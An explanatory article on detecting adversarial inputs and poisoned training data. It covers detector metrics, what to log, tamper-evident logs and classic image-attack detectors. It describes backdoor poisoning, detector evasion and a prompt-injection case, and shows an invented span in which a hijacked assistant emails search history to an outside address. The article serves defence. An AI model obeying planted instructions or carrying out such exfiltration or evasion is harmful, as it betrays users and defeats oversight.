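# Logging and scoring AI model behaviour to detect adversarial inputs and poisoned training data

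## The two attacks, and how a detector is measured

Attack detection in machine learning means watching what a model does, in training or in use, for signs that someone is manipulating it. Many detectors store a log of the model's inputs, outputs, internal states, tool calls or training steps, compute a score from the log, and raise an alarm when the score is high.

Defenders use such detectors against two kinds of attack. An adversarial input causes a trained model to give a wrong or forbidden response. In data poisoning, the attacker adds or alters training examples so that the resulting model misbehaves.

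### How a model learns

A neural network is a long series of arithmetic operations with adjustable numbers called parameters. To train it, a developer feeds it examples with known answers, such as a photograph labelled "stop sign" or a passage of text whose next word is known. A loss function measures the gap between the model's answer and the right one as a single number. A common choice is the negative natural logarithm of the probability that the model assigned to the right answer. This loss is about 0.1 when the probability is 0.9 and about 4.6 when it is 0.01. The training algorithm adjusts the parameters slightly to lower the loss, then repeats this over the whole training set, often many millions of times.

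As the network processes an input, each layer computes intermediate numbers called activations. These differ from one input to the next, while the parameters stay fixed once training ends. Some detectors score the loss on a training example, and others score the activations an input produces, often with a probe, which is a small classifier trained on activations.

### An input that fools a finished model

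In the textbook example, researchers put black and white stickers on real road signs, and an image classifier misread signs that any driver would still have recognised. That experiment is several years old and used an earlier generation of classifier. *Adversarial Machine Learning* (Vassilev, Oprea and colleagues, 2025), a taxonomy from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), also describes a case from a commercial product. A company ran a detector of phishing pages, the fake login pages that steal passwords, and sent images its models could not classify with confidence to human analysts. Among 4,600 such images, researchers found 100 adversarial ones. The attackers had made these without sophisticated computation, by cropping, masking or blurring parts of the page.

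A language model's input is text, and attacks through it take two main forms. In a jailbreak, the user writes a prompt that gets the model to do something its developer trained it to refuse. In a prompt injection, the user is innocent, and the attacker plants instructions in something the model reads, such as a web page or an email. *When Benchmarks Lie* (Fomin, 2026) gives an example from a public test set. A user asks an assistant for the details of a laptop, and the product data it retrieves include a request to email the user's search history to an outside address, which an assistant that can send email may do.

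### Training examples that plant a backdoor

A backdoor is a planted behaviour that appears only in the presence of a trigger, which is a pattern, word or context that the attacker chose. BadNets (2017), the first published example, added a small patch to some training images and changed their labels to a chosen class. The classifier learned to link the patch with that class, and afterwards misclassified any image that carried it.

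Language models learn from text on the public web, where anyone can publish, so the practical question is how much poisoned text an attacker needs. Earlier work assumed the attacker must poison a fixed share of the training data, such as 0.1%, which is an enormous amount of text for a large model. Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, found that the share hardly matters. They trained models of 600 million to 13 billion parameters from scratch, with 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents scattered through the training data. Each document contained ordinary text, then the trigger, then gibberish.

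With 250 documents, models of every size learned to produce gibberish after the trigger and write normally without it, but the attack failed with 100. The largest model was trained on more than twenty times as much clean text as the smallest, and this did not weaken the effect. The 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the largest model's training tokens, the words and word fragments that a model splits text into.

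The researchers chose gibberish, a fairly harmless payload, because they could measure it during training. In a separate experiment they fine-tuned (trained further) an existing 8-billion-parameter model to comply with harmful requests only when the trigger was present, and again the absolute number of examples determined whether the attack worked. Thirteen billion parameters is small beside current frontier models, so assuming that the number stays constant at frontier scale is an extrapolation. Ordinary testing is unlikely to find such a backdoor because the testers do not know the trigger.

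### From a record to an alarm

Detecting either attack takes four steps. The defender records something about an item *x*, which may be one request, a whole session or a training example. A function *f* turns the record into a score *f(x)*, designed to be higher for attacks than for normal use. The detector flags *x* if the score reaches a threshold *θ*. Once *x* is flagged, software blocks the answer, an analyst reads the session, or a developer drops the training example.

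Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, follow this pattern for agents, which are language models that carry out tasks by calling tools such as mail clients. They score the ordered log, or trace, of each session once, after the session ends, and an alert sends the session to an analyst. This audit can therefore find hijacked sessions but not prevent them. They set each detector's threshold on training data, at the level that flags 80% of the known attacks. On new sessions from the same benchmark, one detector caught 77% of attacks and another caught 68%, both below the 80% target. Rao, Keller and colleagues (2026), in *Challenges to the Monitoring of Deployed AI Systems*, a NIST study based on workshops and a literature review, describe validated methods for monitoring deployed systems as still at an early stage.

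Four measures describe how well a detector works. The true positive rate, or detection rate, is the share of attacks it flags. The false positive rate is the share of harmless cases it flags. Precision is the share of flagged cases that are real attacks. These three depend on where the threshold is set. Suppose, for example, that four attacks score 0.9, 0.8, 0.6 and 0.4, and five harmless requests score 0.7, 0.5, 0.3, 0.2 and 0.1.

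| Threshold | True positive rate | False positive rate | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.75 | 2 of 4 (50%) | 0 of 5 (0%) | 2 of 2 (100%) |
| 0.55 | 3 of 4 (75%) | 1 of 5 (20%) | 3 of 4 (75%) |
| 0.35 | 4 of 4 (100%) | 2 of 5 (40%) | 4 of 6 (67%) |

Lowering the threshold catches more attacks but also flags more harmless requests. No threshold in the example avoids both errors, because the scores of attacks and harmless requests overlap. Plotting the true positive rate against the false positive rate at every possible threshold gives the receiver operating characteristic (ROC) curve. The fourth measure is the area under this curve, or AUROC, which equals the probability that a random attack scores higher than a random harmless request. An AUROC of 0.5 is no better than chance, and 1 means perfect separation. The example has 20 possible pairs of one attack and one harmless request, and the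 attack scores higher in 17, so the AUROC is 0.85.

The AUROC is convenient for comparing detectors because it does not require choosing a threshold. For the same reason, it does not measure how a detector performs at the threshold a defender uses.

### When attacks are rare

The true and false positive rates come from attacks alone and harmless cases alone. As *Confidently Wrong* (2026) points out for detectors of prompt injection, neither rate changes with how common attacks are, though the risk in deployment does. Precision changes too. If *π* is the share of all cases that are attacks (the base rate), then

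precision = (*π* × true positive rate) / (*π* × true positive rate + (1 − *π*) × false positive rate).

If a service receives 1,000,000 requests and 10 are attacks, a detector with a 95% true positive rate and a 1% false positive rate will flag about 9.5 attacks and 10,000 harmless requests. Its precision is only about 0.1%, so an analyst would read roughly a thousand harmless requests for each real attack.

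Cutting the false positive rate tenfold, to 0.1%, leaves about 1,000 false alarms and a precision of about 0.9%. Catching all ten attacks instead of 9.5 would barely raise the precision. For half the alarms to be real, the false positive rate would have to fall to about 0.001%, or one harmless request in 100,000.

Axelsson described the base-rate effect for network intrusion detection in 2000. Abbasi and colleagues measured it on agent traces at a far less extreme attack rate, 2% of sessions. One of their detectors had an AUROC of 0.879, which many papers would report as a good result. At its threshold, it raised about 200 alerts per 1,000 sessions, with 12.2 false alerts for every true one, a precision of 7.6%. They calculated that precision would fall to 0.4% at an attack rate of 0.1%.

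A defender can sometimes raise the base rate of attacks by checking fewer things. *Evaluating Deception, Not Just Deepfakes* (2026) gives the example of a defence that stops 900 of 1,000 attacks and interrupts 990 harmless interactions, where attacks are 1% of the total. Its precision is 47.6%. If attacks become ten times rarer, the defence needs a false positive rate ten times lower to keep about the same precision. Checking only high-value decisions, such as large money transfers, raises the share of attacks among the cases checked. It also makes false alarms easier to justify, since a needless phone call before a large transfer does much less harm than a theft.

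Errors have different consequences again when a detector filters training data. Suppose a filter with the same rates, catching 95% of poisoned documents and wrongly flagging 1% of clean ones, runs over a corpus that holds 250 poisoned documents. Nearly everything it flags will be clean, but the developer loses only about 1% of the corpus and nobody has to read the flagged documents. About 12 poisoned documents remain, well below the 100 that were too few for the attack to work in Souly and colleagues' experiments, so the filter may be worth running despite its very low precision. The protection is limited, though, because an attacker able to plant 5,000 documents would still have about 250 left.

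### What the test data can hide

A false positive rate depends on the harmless cases used to measure it. The detector with the AUROC of 0.879 flagged 11.8% of ordinary harmless sessions, but 38.7% of the benchmark's "hard negatives", harmless sessions that are difficult to tell from attacks. If 2% of sessions are attacks, its precision is 11.7% when all the harmless sessions are ordinary and 3.9% when all are hard negatives. A company whose normal traffic looks odd, for example because its staff test security software, should expect the lower precision.

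The test set also has to be large enough. Another detector in the same study flagged none of 825 harmless sessions, which statistically rules out only false positive rates above about 0.4%. In the service with 10 attacks per million requests, a 0.4% rate would mean about 4,000 false alarms per million. To show with 95% confidence that the rate is below 0.001%, a tester would need around 300,000 harmless cases with no alarms. Published test sets are seldom built for this. In the eleven evaluations of agent detectors that Abbasi and colleagues audited, attacks or anomalies made up 16% to 86% of the mixed test sets, and none of the evaluations varied that share.

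Drawing training and test examples from the same sources can also inflate a detector's score. Fomin trained probes on the activations of an 8-billion-parameter language model, using 18 datasets of malicious and harmless prompts. With the usual method, which splits each dataset between training and testing, the AUROC was 0.996. When he held out each whole dataset in turn and tested on it, the AUROC fell to 0.912. Several of the datasets contained only attacks or only harmless text, so a classifier could score well by recognising where a prompt came from. A separate classifier identified the correct dataset 96.6% of the time. An AUROC of 0.912 is still far above chance, but its distance from 1 is more than twenty times larger than under the usual test.

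### Attackers who know the detector

All of these measurements use a fixed set of attacks, but a real attacker can choose which attack to use. An attacker who knows how the detector works can also design an attack to avoid it, which is called an adaptive attack. The average detection rate over past attacks is then a poor guide to how well the detector will perform, since the attacker will use whichever attack it catches least often.

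Defences have a poor record under such testing. Vassilev and colleagues report that Carlini and Wagner bypassed ten methods for detecting adversarial inputs, and that Tramèr and colleagues later bypassed thirteen defences. Both results predate 2025 and concern older models, but the pattern has continued with language models. Fomin notes that in 2025 Nasr and colleagues bypassed twelve recent defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection.

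A detector of this kind is vulnerable because its score depends on features of the log, and the attacker writes part of the log. One of the agent detectors Abbasi and colleagues tested relied heavily on a feature the attacker controls directly. When they altered only that feature and left the threshold unchanged, the detection rate fell from 77.1% to 3.3%.

They did not check whether the altered attacks would still have hijacked the agent. A change that hides an attack can also stop it from working, so a full test also reports the attack success rate, which is the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal with the defence on. Only one of the eleven evaluations in their audit tested adaptive attackers.

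## What is recorded, and whether the record can be trusted

A company that runs its own model can log almost everything the model computes, while one that rents a model over the internet receives little besides text. The choice of detector therefore depends first on who runs the model, and then on how much each part of the log costs to keep.

### The layers of a log

Request metadata is the smallest layer of the record, at a few hundred bytes per request. It includes the time, account, session, model version and number of tokens. A detector can use it to count how often each account queries the model, but not to tell a malicious prompt from a harmless one of the same length. Customers can log only their own requests, so only the operator of the service can link the requests in an attack spread over many accounts. Where users do not log in, OWASP's *Input threats*, part of a free AI security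 guide from a non-profit software-security group, suggests approximating identity by network address or device. It also recommends logging each change of model or prompt, because these events help to reconstruct an incident and can be signs of a break-in.

The next layer is the text of inputs and outputs. A thousand tokens of English take up about 4 kilobytes, so a service that handles a million requests of that length a day would store about 4 gigabytes daily. This storage is cheap, and either the provider or the customer can keep the log. The bigger drawback is the risk to privacy. Many assistants also retrieve documents from a store and add them to the prompt. For these, OWASP recommends logging the identity of each retrieved passage, so that an investigator can trace a prompt injection to the document that contained it and the account that added the document.

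Confidence values are the probabilities a model assigns to its possible answers. They show whether another answer was almost as probable as the one the model gave, which can't be seen from the answer alone. An image classifier with 1,000 classes produces 1,000 values per image, or about 4 kilobytes at four bytes each. A language model produces one value for every token in its vocabulary each time it generates a token. With a vocabulary of 128,000 tokens and two bytes per value, that is 256 kilobytes per output token, so in practice operators keep only the values for the few most likely tokens.

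Attackers also want a model's confidence scores. In a 2019 case from MITRE ATLAS, a public catalogue of AI attacks and countermeasures kept by the US non-profit MITRE, researchers found that a commercial email filter left its model's scores in the headers of the messages it processed. They collected the scores by sending many emails through the filter. An operator can avoid this by logging confidence scores without returning them, but then its customers cannot use them for detection.

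Activations take up far more space than text. A model with about 8 billion parameters typically has 32 layers that each produce 4,096 numbers per token. At two bytes per number, a request of 1,000 tokens yields 262 megabytes, about 65,000 times the size of the text. Few operators would keep all of that, and a probe seldom needs it. One layer's activations at the last token fit in 8 kilobytes. Operators usually compute the score while the model runs and store only the score. To apply a better probe later, they must run the old inputs through the model again, which requires having kept the text and the exact model version.

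A customer of a hosted model usually cannot log its activations, because the provider does not return them. The customer can instead run a smaller open model on the same text and record that model's activations. Those activations may show that a prompt looks like an attack, but not how the hosted model responded to it.

An agent's log also needs to include tool calls. OWASP recommends recording the tool's name, its arguments or a hash (a short fingerprint) of them, the identity the agent acted under, the target, and whether a human approved the call. Some agents keep notes between sessions, and an instruction planted in them can take effect weeks later, so OWASP's list includes the source and time of every write to this memory.

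A tool call shows what the agent requested, while what the machine then did shows up in system calls, the requests that a running program makes to the operating system. If an agent calls a tool that runs a project's tests, the trace may hold a single entry, but the system calls show that one test opened a file of passwords. A single command can generate thousands of system calls. Only the machine's operator can log them, so when a tool runs on another company's server, the agent's owner gets only the result.

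The last layer is the training history: the order in which the model processed the examples, the loss on each one, and checkpoints, which are saved copies of the parameters. A detector can use it to find examples that the model learned unusually fast, or the point in training at which a bad behaviour first appeared. The losses take up about 4 gigabytes per pass over a billion examples. Checkpoints take up much more space. A single checkpoint of a 13-billion-parameter model is 26 gigabytes at two bytes per parameter, so a hundred need 2.6 terabytes, even without the extra numbers required to resume training. Normally only the developer has any of this history, and the history alone does not prove to an outsider that the developer trained on the dataset it names.

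### One tool call as a log entry

Detectors are easier to reuse when different systems write their logs in the same format. OpenTelemetry, an open-source project, publishes such a format for software in general and has extended it to language models and agents. Its basic unit is the span, a timed entry for one operation, and the spans of one session make up a trace.

The table below shows an invented span in the format of OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*. It records the assistant in the earlier laptop example obeying the request planted in the product page and emailing out the user's search history.

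| Field | Example value | Status | Where the value comes from |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trace ID | `4bf92f35` (shortened) | On every span | Logging software |
| Start and end | 14:03:07.12 to 14:03:07.91 | On every span | The machine's clock |
| Span name | `execute_tool send_email` | Recommended | Logging software |
| `gen_ai.operation.name` | `execute_tool` | Required | Logging software |
| `gen_ai.tool.name` | `send_email` | Recommended | The model, from the developer's list of tools |
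| `gen_ai.tool.type` | `function` | Recommended if available | The developer |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.id` | `call_81c` | Recommended if available | The model service |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` | `{"to": "archive@example.com", "body": "Recent searches: ..."}` | Opt-in | The model, here following the attacker |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.result` | `{"status": "sent"}` | Opt-in | The tool |
| `error.type` | (absent) | Required if the call fails | Logging software |

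Most of the evidence is in the two opt-in fields. Under the default settings, this log would show that the assistant sent an email at 14:03, but not the recipient or the contents. A detector could still flag the email as unusual, because a question about a laptop does not normally lead to one, but it could not determine whether the user had asked for a copy of the answer.

OpenTelemetry leaves content out by default because it is often large and sensitive. Developers can record it in the spans, which OpenTelemetry suggests for settings such as testing before release, or keep it in a separate store and put only a reference in the span. A separate store suits live systems better because an engineer looking for slow requests can then read the spans without being able to read users' conversations.

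OpenTelemetry's format is still changing. Greptime (2026), a database company, reports that version 1.37 replaced the field `gen_ai.system` with `gen_ai.provider.name`, and that since version 1.41 the name of a tool-call span must include the tool. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, notes that the project moved these conventions to a separate repository in June 2026, and that the repository had no official release by 21 August. Field names also differ between products. The documentation of Axiom, a logging vendor, lists a tool's arguments under `gen_ai.tool.arguments`, whereas OpenTelemetry uses `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments`. A detector that looks only for OpenTelemetry's name would find nothing there and would treat the session as harmless unless someone checks for missing fields.

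### Missing entries and private data

The evidence on how logging goes wrong in practice is mostly testimony. Rao and colleagues gathered it for *NIST AI 800-4*, published in March 2026. They held three online workshops in April and May 2025: one with 33 experts from federal agencies, one with 26 outside experts, and one with 157 members of a NIST consortium. (The study gives a total of over 250 participants, but these figures add up to 216.) They also reviewed 87 papers, starting with 23 and finding the rest through citations and participants' suggestions. Two reviewers sorted the workshop statements by theme, working from notes because nobody had recorded the sessions. This method can show which problems practitioners recognise, but not how often those problems occur or how many attacks go undetected because of them.

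The main barrier to logging they report is that an AI product may run on many machines belonging to several companies, each of which holds part of the record. Participants also complained that they could not see what outside applications did with their data, or which AI services their staff used through personal accounts. When many agents work at once, delays between machines make it impossible to capture the state of every agent at the same instant.

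Some gaps in the record come from where the logging software sits. Many companies route their requests to models through a gateway, a single program that can log all of them. Wang points out that a gateway does not record calls that bypass it or tools that run inside the application. OWASP describes the same problem for document stores, where the program that normally adds documents cannot log what someone writes to the store directly. An attacker who finds such a route can avoid the detector without any special technique.

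To save money, operators often keep only a random fraction of traces, which is fine for measuring average speed but poor for finding rare attacks. If 10 of a million requests are attacks, a 1% sample has only about a 10% chance of containing any of them. Sampling also breaks up attacks that consist of many related queries. If 200 such queries are sampled separately at 1%, about two will remain.

An operator can wait until each session ends and keep every one that used a risky tool, but it must store all sessions temporarily until then. OpenTelemetry recommends that software that sends content to a separate store do so even when the sampler drops the span. But its conventions also let software shorten long messages, which may cut off an instruction at the end of a long web page.

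Keeping everything creates a different risk, because a complete log contains whatever users have typed, which can include details of their health, their finances and their employers' plans. Removing names is not enough to protect their privacy. Rao and colleagues cite work by Chan and colleagues on agent identifiers, which found that timestamps and details of an agent's activity could help an outsider identify its user. Privacy law and contracts can also stop companies from sharing logs, even when they face the same attacker.

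A log of a model's full input can leak the documents in the store, so OWASP recommends logging a hash of each retrieved passage instead of its text. Equal hashes show that two sessions retrieved the same passage. But an investigator cannot search a hash for hidden instructions and still needs the original document. Hashing also gives little protection to short, guessable values such as email addresses, because anyone with a list of addresses can hash each one and look for matches.

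### Checking for tampering

Intruders have good reason to edit the log, and an agent with access to the machine it runs on may be able to edit it too. OWASP therefore recommends storing the record of an agent's actions where the agent cannot modify it and any change can be detected.

Hash chaining is a common way to reveal changes. A hash function turns data of any length into a short, fixed-length value, and the same data always give the same value. In a chain, the logging software computes the hash of each entry from the entry's contents together with the previous entry's hash. Writing *eₙ* for the contents of entry *n* and *hₙ* for its hash,

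*hₙ* = *H*(*hₙ₋₁*, *eₙ*).

In a toy example, the hash function multiplies the previous hash by 31, adds the number in the new entry, and keeps the last three digits. The chain starts from an agreed value of 7.

| Entry | Contents | Calculation | Hash |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Agent read 12 files | 31 × 7 + 12 = 229 | 229 |
| 2 | Agent sent 40 emails | 31 × 229 + 40 = 7,139 | 139 |
| 3 | Agent deleted 5 files | 31 × 139 + 5 = 4,314 | 314 |

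Suppose an intruder changes 40 emails to 4 in entry 2. The hash of entry 2 should now be 103, which does not match the stored 139. If the intruder changes the stored hash to 103, the hash of entry 3 should be 198, which does not match the stored 314. Deleting entry 2 also breaks the chain, because entry 3 would then need a hash of 104.

An intruder who can rewrite the whole log can also recompute every hash, so the forged chain will be consistent. The defender therefore sends the latest hash at regular intervals to a separate machine or an outside party. With a stored copy of the latest hash, 314, the defender can detect both the forgery and the removal of entries from the end. The toy function is insecure because any two numbers that differ by 1,000 give the same result. For a real function such as SHA-256, nobody knows a practical way to find a second entry with the same hash.

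The hash chain shows whether anyone has altered the log since the software wrote it, but not whether the log was complete or true to begin with. If the agent sends an email through a route that nobody logs, there is no entry to hash and no break in the chain. If compromised software writes "sent 4 emails" when the agent sent 40, the false entry still gets a valid hash. The defender needs a record from another source, such as the mail server's own log, to catch either problem.

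OWASP describes a stricter scheme that gives each event a digital signature and a timestamp from an independent authority, so that even the holder of the signing key cannot backdate an entry. For AI systems, the signature should cover the input, model version and settings as well as the output, because the same input can produce different outputs and a signed output alone proves little about what led to it.

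### When the attacker writes part of the log

Even a complete and unaltered log can contain text that an attacker wrote. In the tool call above, the logging software supplied the time, but the recipient's address came from the product page. This makes the time harder to fake, though an attacker may still influence when the agent acts.

Stored text can also be dangerous to whoever reads it. In older plain-text logs, attackers could forge entries by including line breaks in their input. Storing data in separate fields largely prevents this if the logging software handles special characters correctly. Separate fields do not help when the reader is a language model looking for attacks, because instructions aimed at the agent, or at the monitor itself, work through the meaning of the text rather than its layout. OWASP warns that an agent used for defence is part of the attack surface and needs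 narrow permissions.

A model's written reasoning needs similar caution. Some systems log it, and it can expose a plan that does not match the agent's actions. But the reasoning is also a model output, and OWASP advises investigators to reconstruct inputs, outputs and actions rather than hidden intent. Rao and colleagues list only one barrier specific to security monitoring, which is that a model may behave differently when it can tell that someone is monitoring it, so a clean log may not reflect how it acts at other times. They base this on a few papers and workshop questions, not on measurements of deployed systems.

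### What official documents ask for

The MITRE ATLAS entry on telemetry logging, last revised on 30 June 2026, recommends logging the inputs and outputs of deployed models and, for agents, their intermediate steps, data access, tool use, installation commands and identity. It adds that logging may deter attackers who want to stay unnoticed. A separate entry recommends keeping a full history of each dataset's source and changes, which anyone looking for poisoned examples would need. *Deploying AI Systems Securely*, guidance that the US National Security Agency and partner agencies issued in 2024, calls for logs of inputs, outputs, intermediate states and errors, with automatic alerts.

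OWASP's advice is much more detailed. Besides logging the fields described above, it recommends deciding in advance how to respond to each kind of alert and pausing the routine deletion of old logs once an investigation begins. None of these documents is binding or specifies a detection rate that the log should make possible.

The European Union's AI Act is binding, but its logging rules cover only systems that the Act classes as high-risk, such as those used in hiring or medical devices. Four articles matter here:

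- Article 12 requires that such systems can record events automatically throughout their lifetime. It leaves the choice of fields largely open, except for remote biometric identification, where the minimum includes the time of each use and the input that led to a match.
- Article 15 requires resilience against attack, including, where appropriate, measures to prevent, detect and respond to data poisoning and adversarial inputs.
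- Article 19 requires providers to keep the automatic logs under their control for at least six months, unless other law provides otherwise.
- Article 26 sets the same minimum for deployers, the organisations that use the system, and requires them to monitor its operation.

None of these duties applies yet. *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (National Law Review, July 2026) reports that an amending law in force since 27 July moved the high-risk duties to 2 December 2027 and 2 August 2028. The 2027 date applies to uses listed in the Act, such as hiring and credit scoring, and the 2028 date applies to AI in products that other EU safety laws already regulate.

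OWASP reads Article 12 as expecting records over several years, much longer than the six-month minimum in Articles 19 and 26. Six months is ample for attacks that an operator notices within days. But a backdoor can stay dormant for longer, and a company that kept only the minimum may have deleted the logs of the attacker's first tests by the time the trigger appears.

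## Scoring one input by how a classifier responds to it

The simplest detectors need only one log entry, which records a single input and the classifier's response to it. When an attacker alters a photograph of a stop sign so that a classifier labels it a speed-limit sign, the response often differs from the response to a real speed-limit sign. The label may change when the picture is slightly blurred, or the activations may be unusual for the speed-limit class.

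Researchers developed the best-known detectors of this kind in 2017 and 2018 for image classifiers, which choose one answer from a fixed list of classes. They tested the detectors on public datasets: MNIST (small grey images of handwritten digits), CIFAR-10 (tiny colour images of ten kinds of object), SVHN (photographs of house numbers) and ImageNet (larger photographs in 1,000 classes). The networks were far smaller than current models, so the detection rates below are of historical interest, but the scores are still in use.

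Feature squeezing needs only the classifier's confidence values, while Mahalanobis distance and local intrinsic dimensionality need its activations.

### Feature squeezing

A grey pixel in a standard image can take 256 values, many more than anyone needs to recognise a digit. Xu, Evans and Qi (2017), in *Feature Squeezing*, argued that this surplus detail leaves attackers room for changes that people do not notice. Their detector removes some of the detail and measures how far the classifier's output moves:

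1. Run the classifier on the original image and record the probability of each class.
2. Make simplified copies of the image. One copy has fewer colour levels. Another goes through a median filter, which replaces each pixel with the median of its neighbours. For colour images, a third copy averages patches that look alike.
3. Run the classifier on each copy.
4. For each copy, add up the absolute changes in probability over all classes. The largest total is the score.

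Writing *pⱼ(x)* for the probability of class *j* and *s(x)* for a simplified copy,

score(*x*) = max over *s* of Σⱼ | *pⱼ(x)* − *pⱼ(s(x))* |.

The score is 0 when the probabilities do not change, and 2 when the classifier assigns a probability of 1 to one class before the simplification and to a different class after it. The table below uses invented probabilities for a classifier with three classes.

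| Image | Version | Stop | Speed limit | Give way | Total change |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary stop sign | Original | 0.92 | 0.05 | 0.03 | |
| | Fewer colours | 0.90 | 0.06 | 0.04 | 0.04 |
| | Median filter | 0.80 | 0.12 | 0.08 | 0.24 |
| Altered stop sign | Original | 0.05 | 0.90 | 0.05 | |
| | Fewer colours | 0.60 | 0.30 | 0.10 | 1.20 |
| | Median filter | 0.85 | 0.10 | 0.05 | 1.60 |

For the last row, the total is |0.05 − 0.85| + |0.90 − 0.10| + |0.05 − 0.05| = 1.60. The ordinary image scores 0.24 and the altered one 1.60, so a threshold of 1 separates them.

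Taking the largest total helps because different copies undo different attacks. Reducing the colours removes tiny changes to many pixels, while the median filter removes large changes to a few. But for a harmless image, the largest total comes from whichever copy damaged it most, which raises the false positive rate.

Xu and colleagues chose each threshold so that no more than 5% of the harmless images in their training half scored above it. They tested the detector on the other half, using eleven attacks that were not designed to evade it. It flagged 98% of the successful attacks on MNIST with a false positive rate of 4.0%, 85% on CIFAR-10 with 4.9%, and 86% on ImageNet with 8.3%, which is above the 5% target.

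The detection rates behind these averages vary widely by attack. On CIFAR-10 the detector caught every successful example of a strong attack that searches for the smallest change that causes a misclassification, but only 21% of those made by the fast gradient sign method, an older and quick one-step attack. Xu and colleagues suspect that the older method is harder to detect because it makes larger changes, which mild simplification does not undo.

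The false positive rates are also high for routine use. If one image in 1,000 is an attack, the CIFAR-10 figures give a precision of about 1.7%, or 58 false alarms for each attack detected. Xu and colleagues tried a stricter threshold when they compared their method with another detector. At a false positive rate of 1.3%, detection on CIFAR-10 fell to 62%, so precision would rise only to about 4.6%. Each test used only about 500 harmless images, too few to measure the much lower rates that a busy service needs.

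### Mahalanobis distance

A classifier can be very confident about an image unlike anything in its training data, because its confidence depends on which side of a class boundary the image falls and how far it is from that boundary. In *A Simple Unified Framework for Detecting Out-of-Distribution Samples and Adversarial Attacks*, Lee, Lee and colleagues (2018) therefore measured how far an image's activations lie from those of the nearest class in the training data.

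The defender first runs the training images through the finished classifier and computes the mean activations *μⱼ* of each class *j*. The next step is to compute a covariance matrix *S*, shared by all classes, which records how much each activation varies around its class mean and how pairs of activations vary together. For a new image with activations *a(x)*, the score is

*d(x)* = min over *j* of (*a(x)* − *μⱼ*)ᵀ *S*⁻¹ (*a(x)* − *μⱼ*).

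This is the squared Mahalanobis distance to the nearest class mean. Lee and colleagues negate it, so a high value means a normal image. Multiplying by the inverse of *S* gives more weight to deviations that are rare in the training data.

Suppose there are only two activations, each with a variance of 1, and that they usually rise and fall together, with a correlation of 0.9. One image is 1 above the class mean on both. Another is 1 above on the first and 1 below on the second. Both are the same straight-line distance from the mean, but their Mahalanobis scores are about 1.05 and 20, because the first image follows the usual pattern and the second breaks it.

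The method assumes that the activations for each class follow a bell-shaped (Gaussian) distribution. Lee and colleagues checked this indirectly by assigning each image to the class with the nearest mean activation, and found about the same accuracy as with the network's own output. That supports the assumption for ordinary images but does not show that every adversarial image falls outside these distributions.

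Two additions improved detection. Before scoring, the software changes the image slightly to bring it closer to the nearest class. In their experiments, this widened the gap between normal and abnormal images. The software also computes a distance at each of several layers and combines the distances with logistic regression, a simple classifier that learns a weight for each one. The defender needs sample attacks to learn those weights.

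On CIFAR-10 with a ResNet, the combined score had an AUROC of 0.958 against Carlini and Wagner's attack, which searches for a small change that produces the wrong answer, and 0.999 against the fast gradient sign method. The comparison of attacks doesn't include false alarms at a chosen threshold.

Detection was weaker when the weights came from one attack and the test used another. When the weights were trained on the fast gradient sign method alone, the AUROC for Carlini and Wagner's attack was still 0.939. For the DeepFool attack, it fell from 0.916 to 0.781, and from 0.957 to 0.722 on the house numbers. DeepFool was a published attack that didn't try to avoid the detector, so even these lower figures are weak evidence of how well the detector would work against an attacker who tried to evade it.

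### Local intrinsic dimensionality

The third score measures how many dimensions the data has around an input. If points are spread evenly over a flat sheet, doubling the radius of a circle multiplies the number of points inside it by four. For a ball in a solid block, the factor is eight, and in *m* dimensions it is 2ᵐ. The number of dimensions around an input can therefore be calculated from how quickly the number of neighbours grows with the radius. For real data, it need not be a whole number.

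Ma, Li and colleagues (2018), in *Characterizing Adversarial Subspaces Using Local Intrinsic Dimensionality*, expected this number to be higher for adversarial images. Ordinary images vary in relatively few ways, so their activations lie near a surface with few dimensions. An attacker can change every pixel independently, which tends to push the image's activations slightly off that surface, where their neighbours come from several different groups of images.

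To estimate the dimensionality, the software measures the distances *r₁*, *r₂*, ..., *rₖ* from the input's activations to its *k* nearest neighbours, in increasing order. The estimate is

LID(*x*) = −1 / [ (1/*k*) Σᵢ ln(*rᵢ* / *rₖ*) ].

With four neighbours at distances 1, 2, 3 and 4, the average logarithm is −0.59 and the estimate is 1.7. With neighbours at 3.4, 3.7, 3.9 and 4, the average is −0.066 and the estimate is 15. The farthest neighbour is at distance 4 in both cases, but the second estimate is higher because all four neighbours are at nearly the same distance, as they are in a space with many dimensions, where most of a ball's volume lies near its edge.

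Ma and colleagues looked for an input's 20 or 30 nearest neighbours in a random batch of 100 ordinary images, because searching the whole training set would be slow. They computed one estimate per layer and trained a logistic regression to combine the estimates. Its training data included ordinary images, adversarial images, and ordinary images with random noise of the same size as the attacker's changes, so that the detector would learn to ignore harmless noise.

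The AUROC against the strongest attack they tried was 0.992 on MNIST, 0.989 on CIFAR-10 and 0.976 on the house numbers. A quick one-step attack on CIFAR-10 was harder to detect, with an AUROC of 0.824. These figures may not hold for another network. When Lee and colleagues ran the same method on ResNet against Carlini and Wagner's attack, its AUROC on CIFAR-10 was 0.822.

Ma and colleagues also discarded every test image that the classifier got wrong before any attack, which removed about 15% of the CIFAR-10 test images. A deployed detector would receive such images, and they are a likely source of false alarms because images that are hard to classify are the most likely to have unusual activations.

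### Re-tests with attackers who know the detector

Almost all the detection figures above come from attacks that were not designed to evade the detector. They show that such attacks seldom find inputs with both a wrong answer and a low score, but not that these inputs are rare.

*Adversarial Examples Are Not Easily Detected* (Carlini and Wagner, 2017) re-tested ten detectors from seven papers. The ten did not include the three described above, though several used related ideas, such as statistical tests on activations or blurring the image. Six did significantly worse than their inventors believed, even against a strong attack that was not designed to evade them. All ten failed against an attacker who knew how they worked and had their parameters. Against this attacker, five added no protection, three added a little, and two helped only on simple datasets. Attackers who knew the type of detector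 but not its parameters also succeeded.

Two of the detectors used a neural network trained on adversarial digits. Both flagged at least 98% of new adversarial digits made by an attacker unaware of the detectors, but an attacker who knew about them succeeded every time, with changes to the image only about 10% larger on average. On CIFAR-10, the detectors caught only 70% of the unaware attacks while flagging 40% of harmless images. Carlini and Wagner concluded that the supposed signs of an adversarial image were specific to the attacks of the time.

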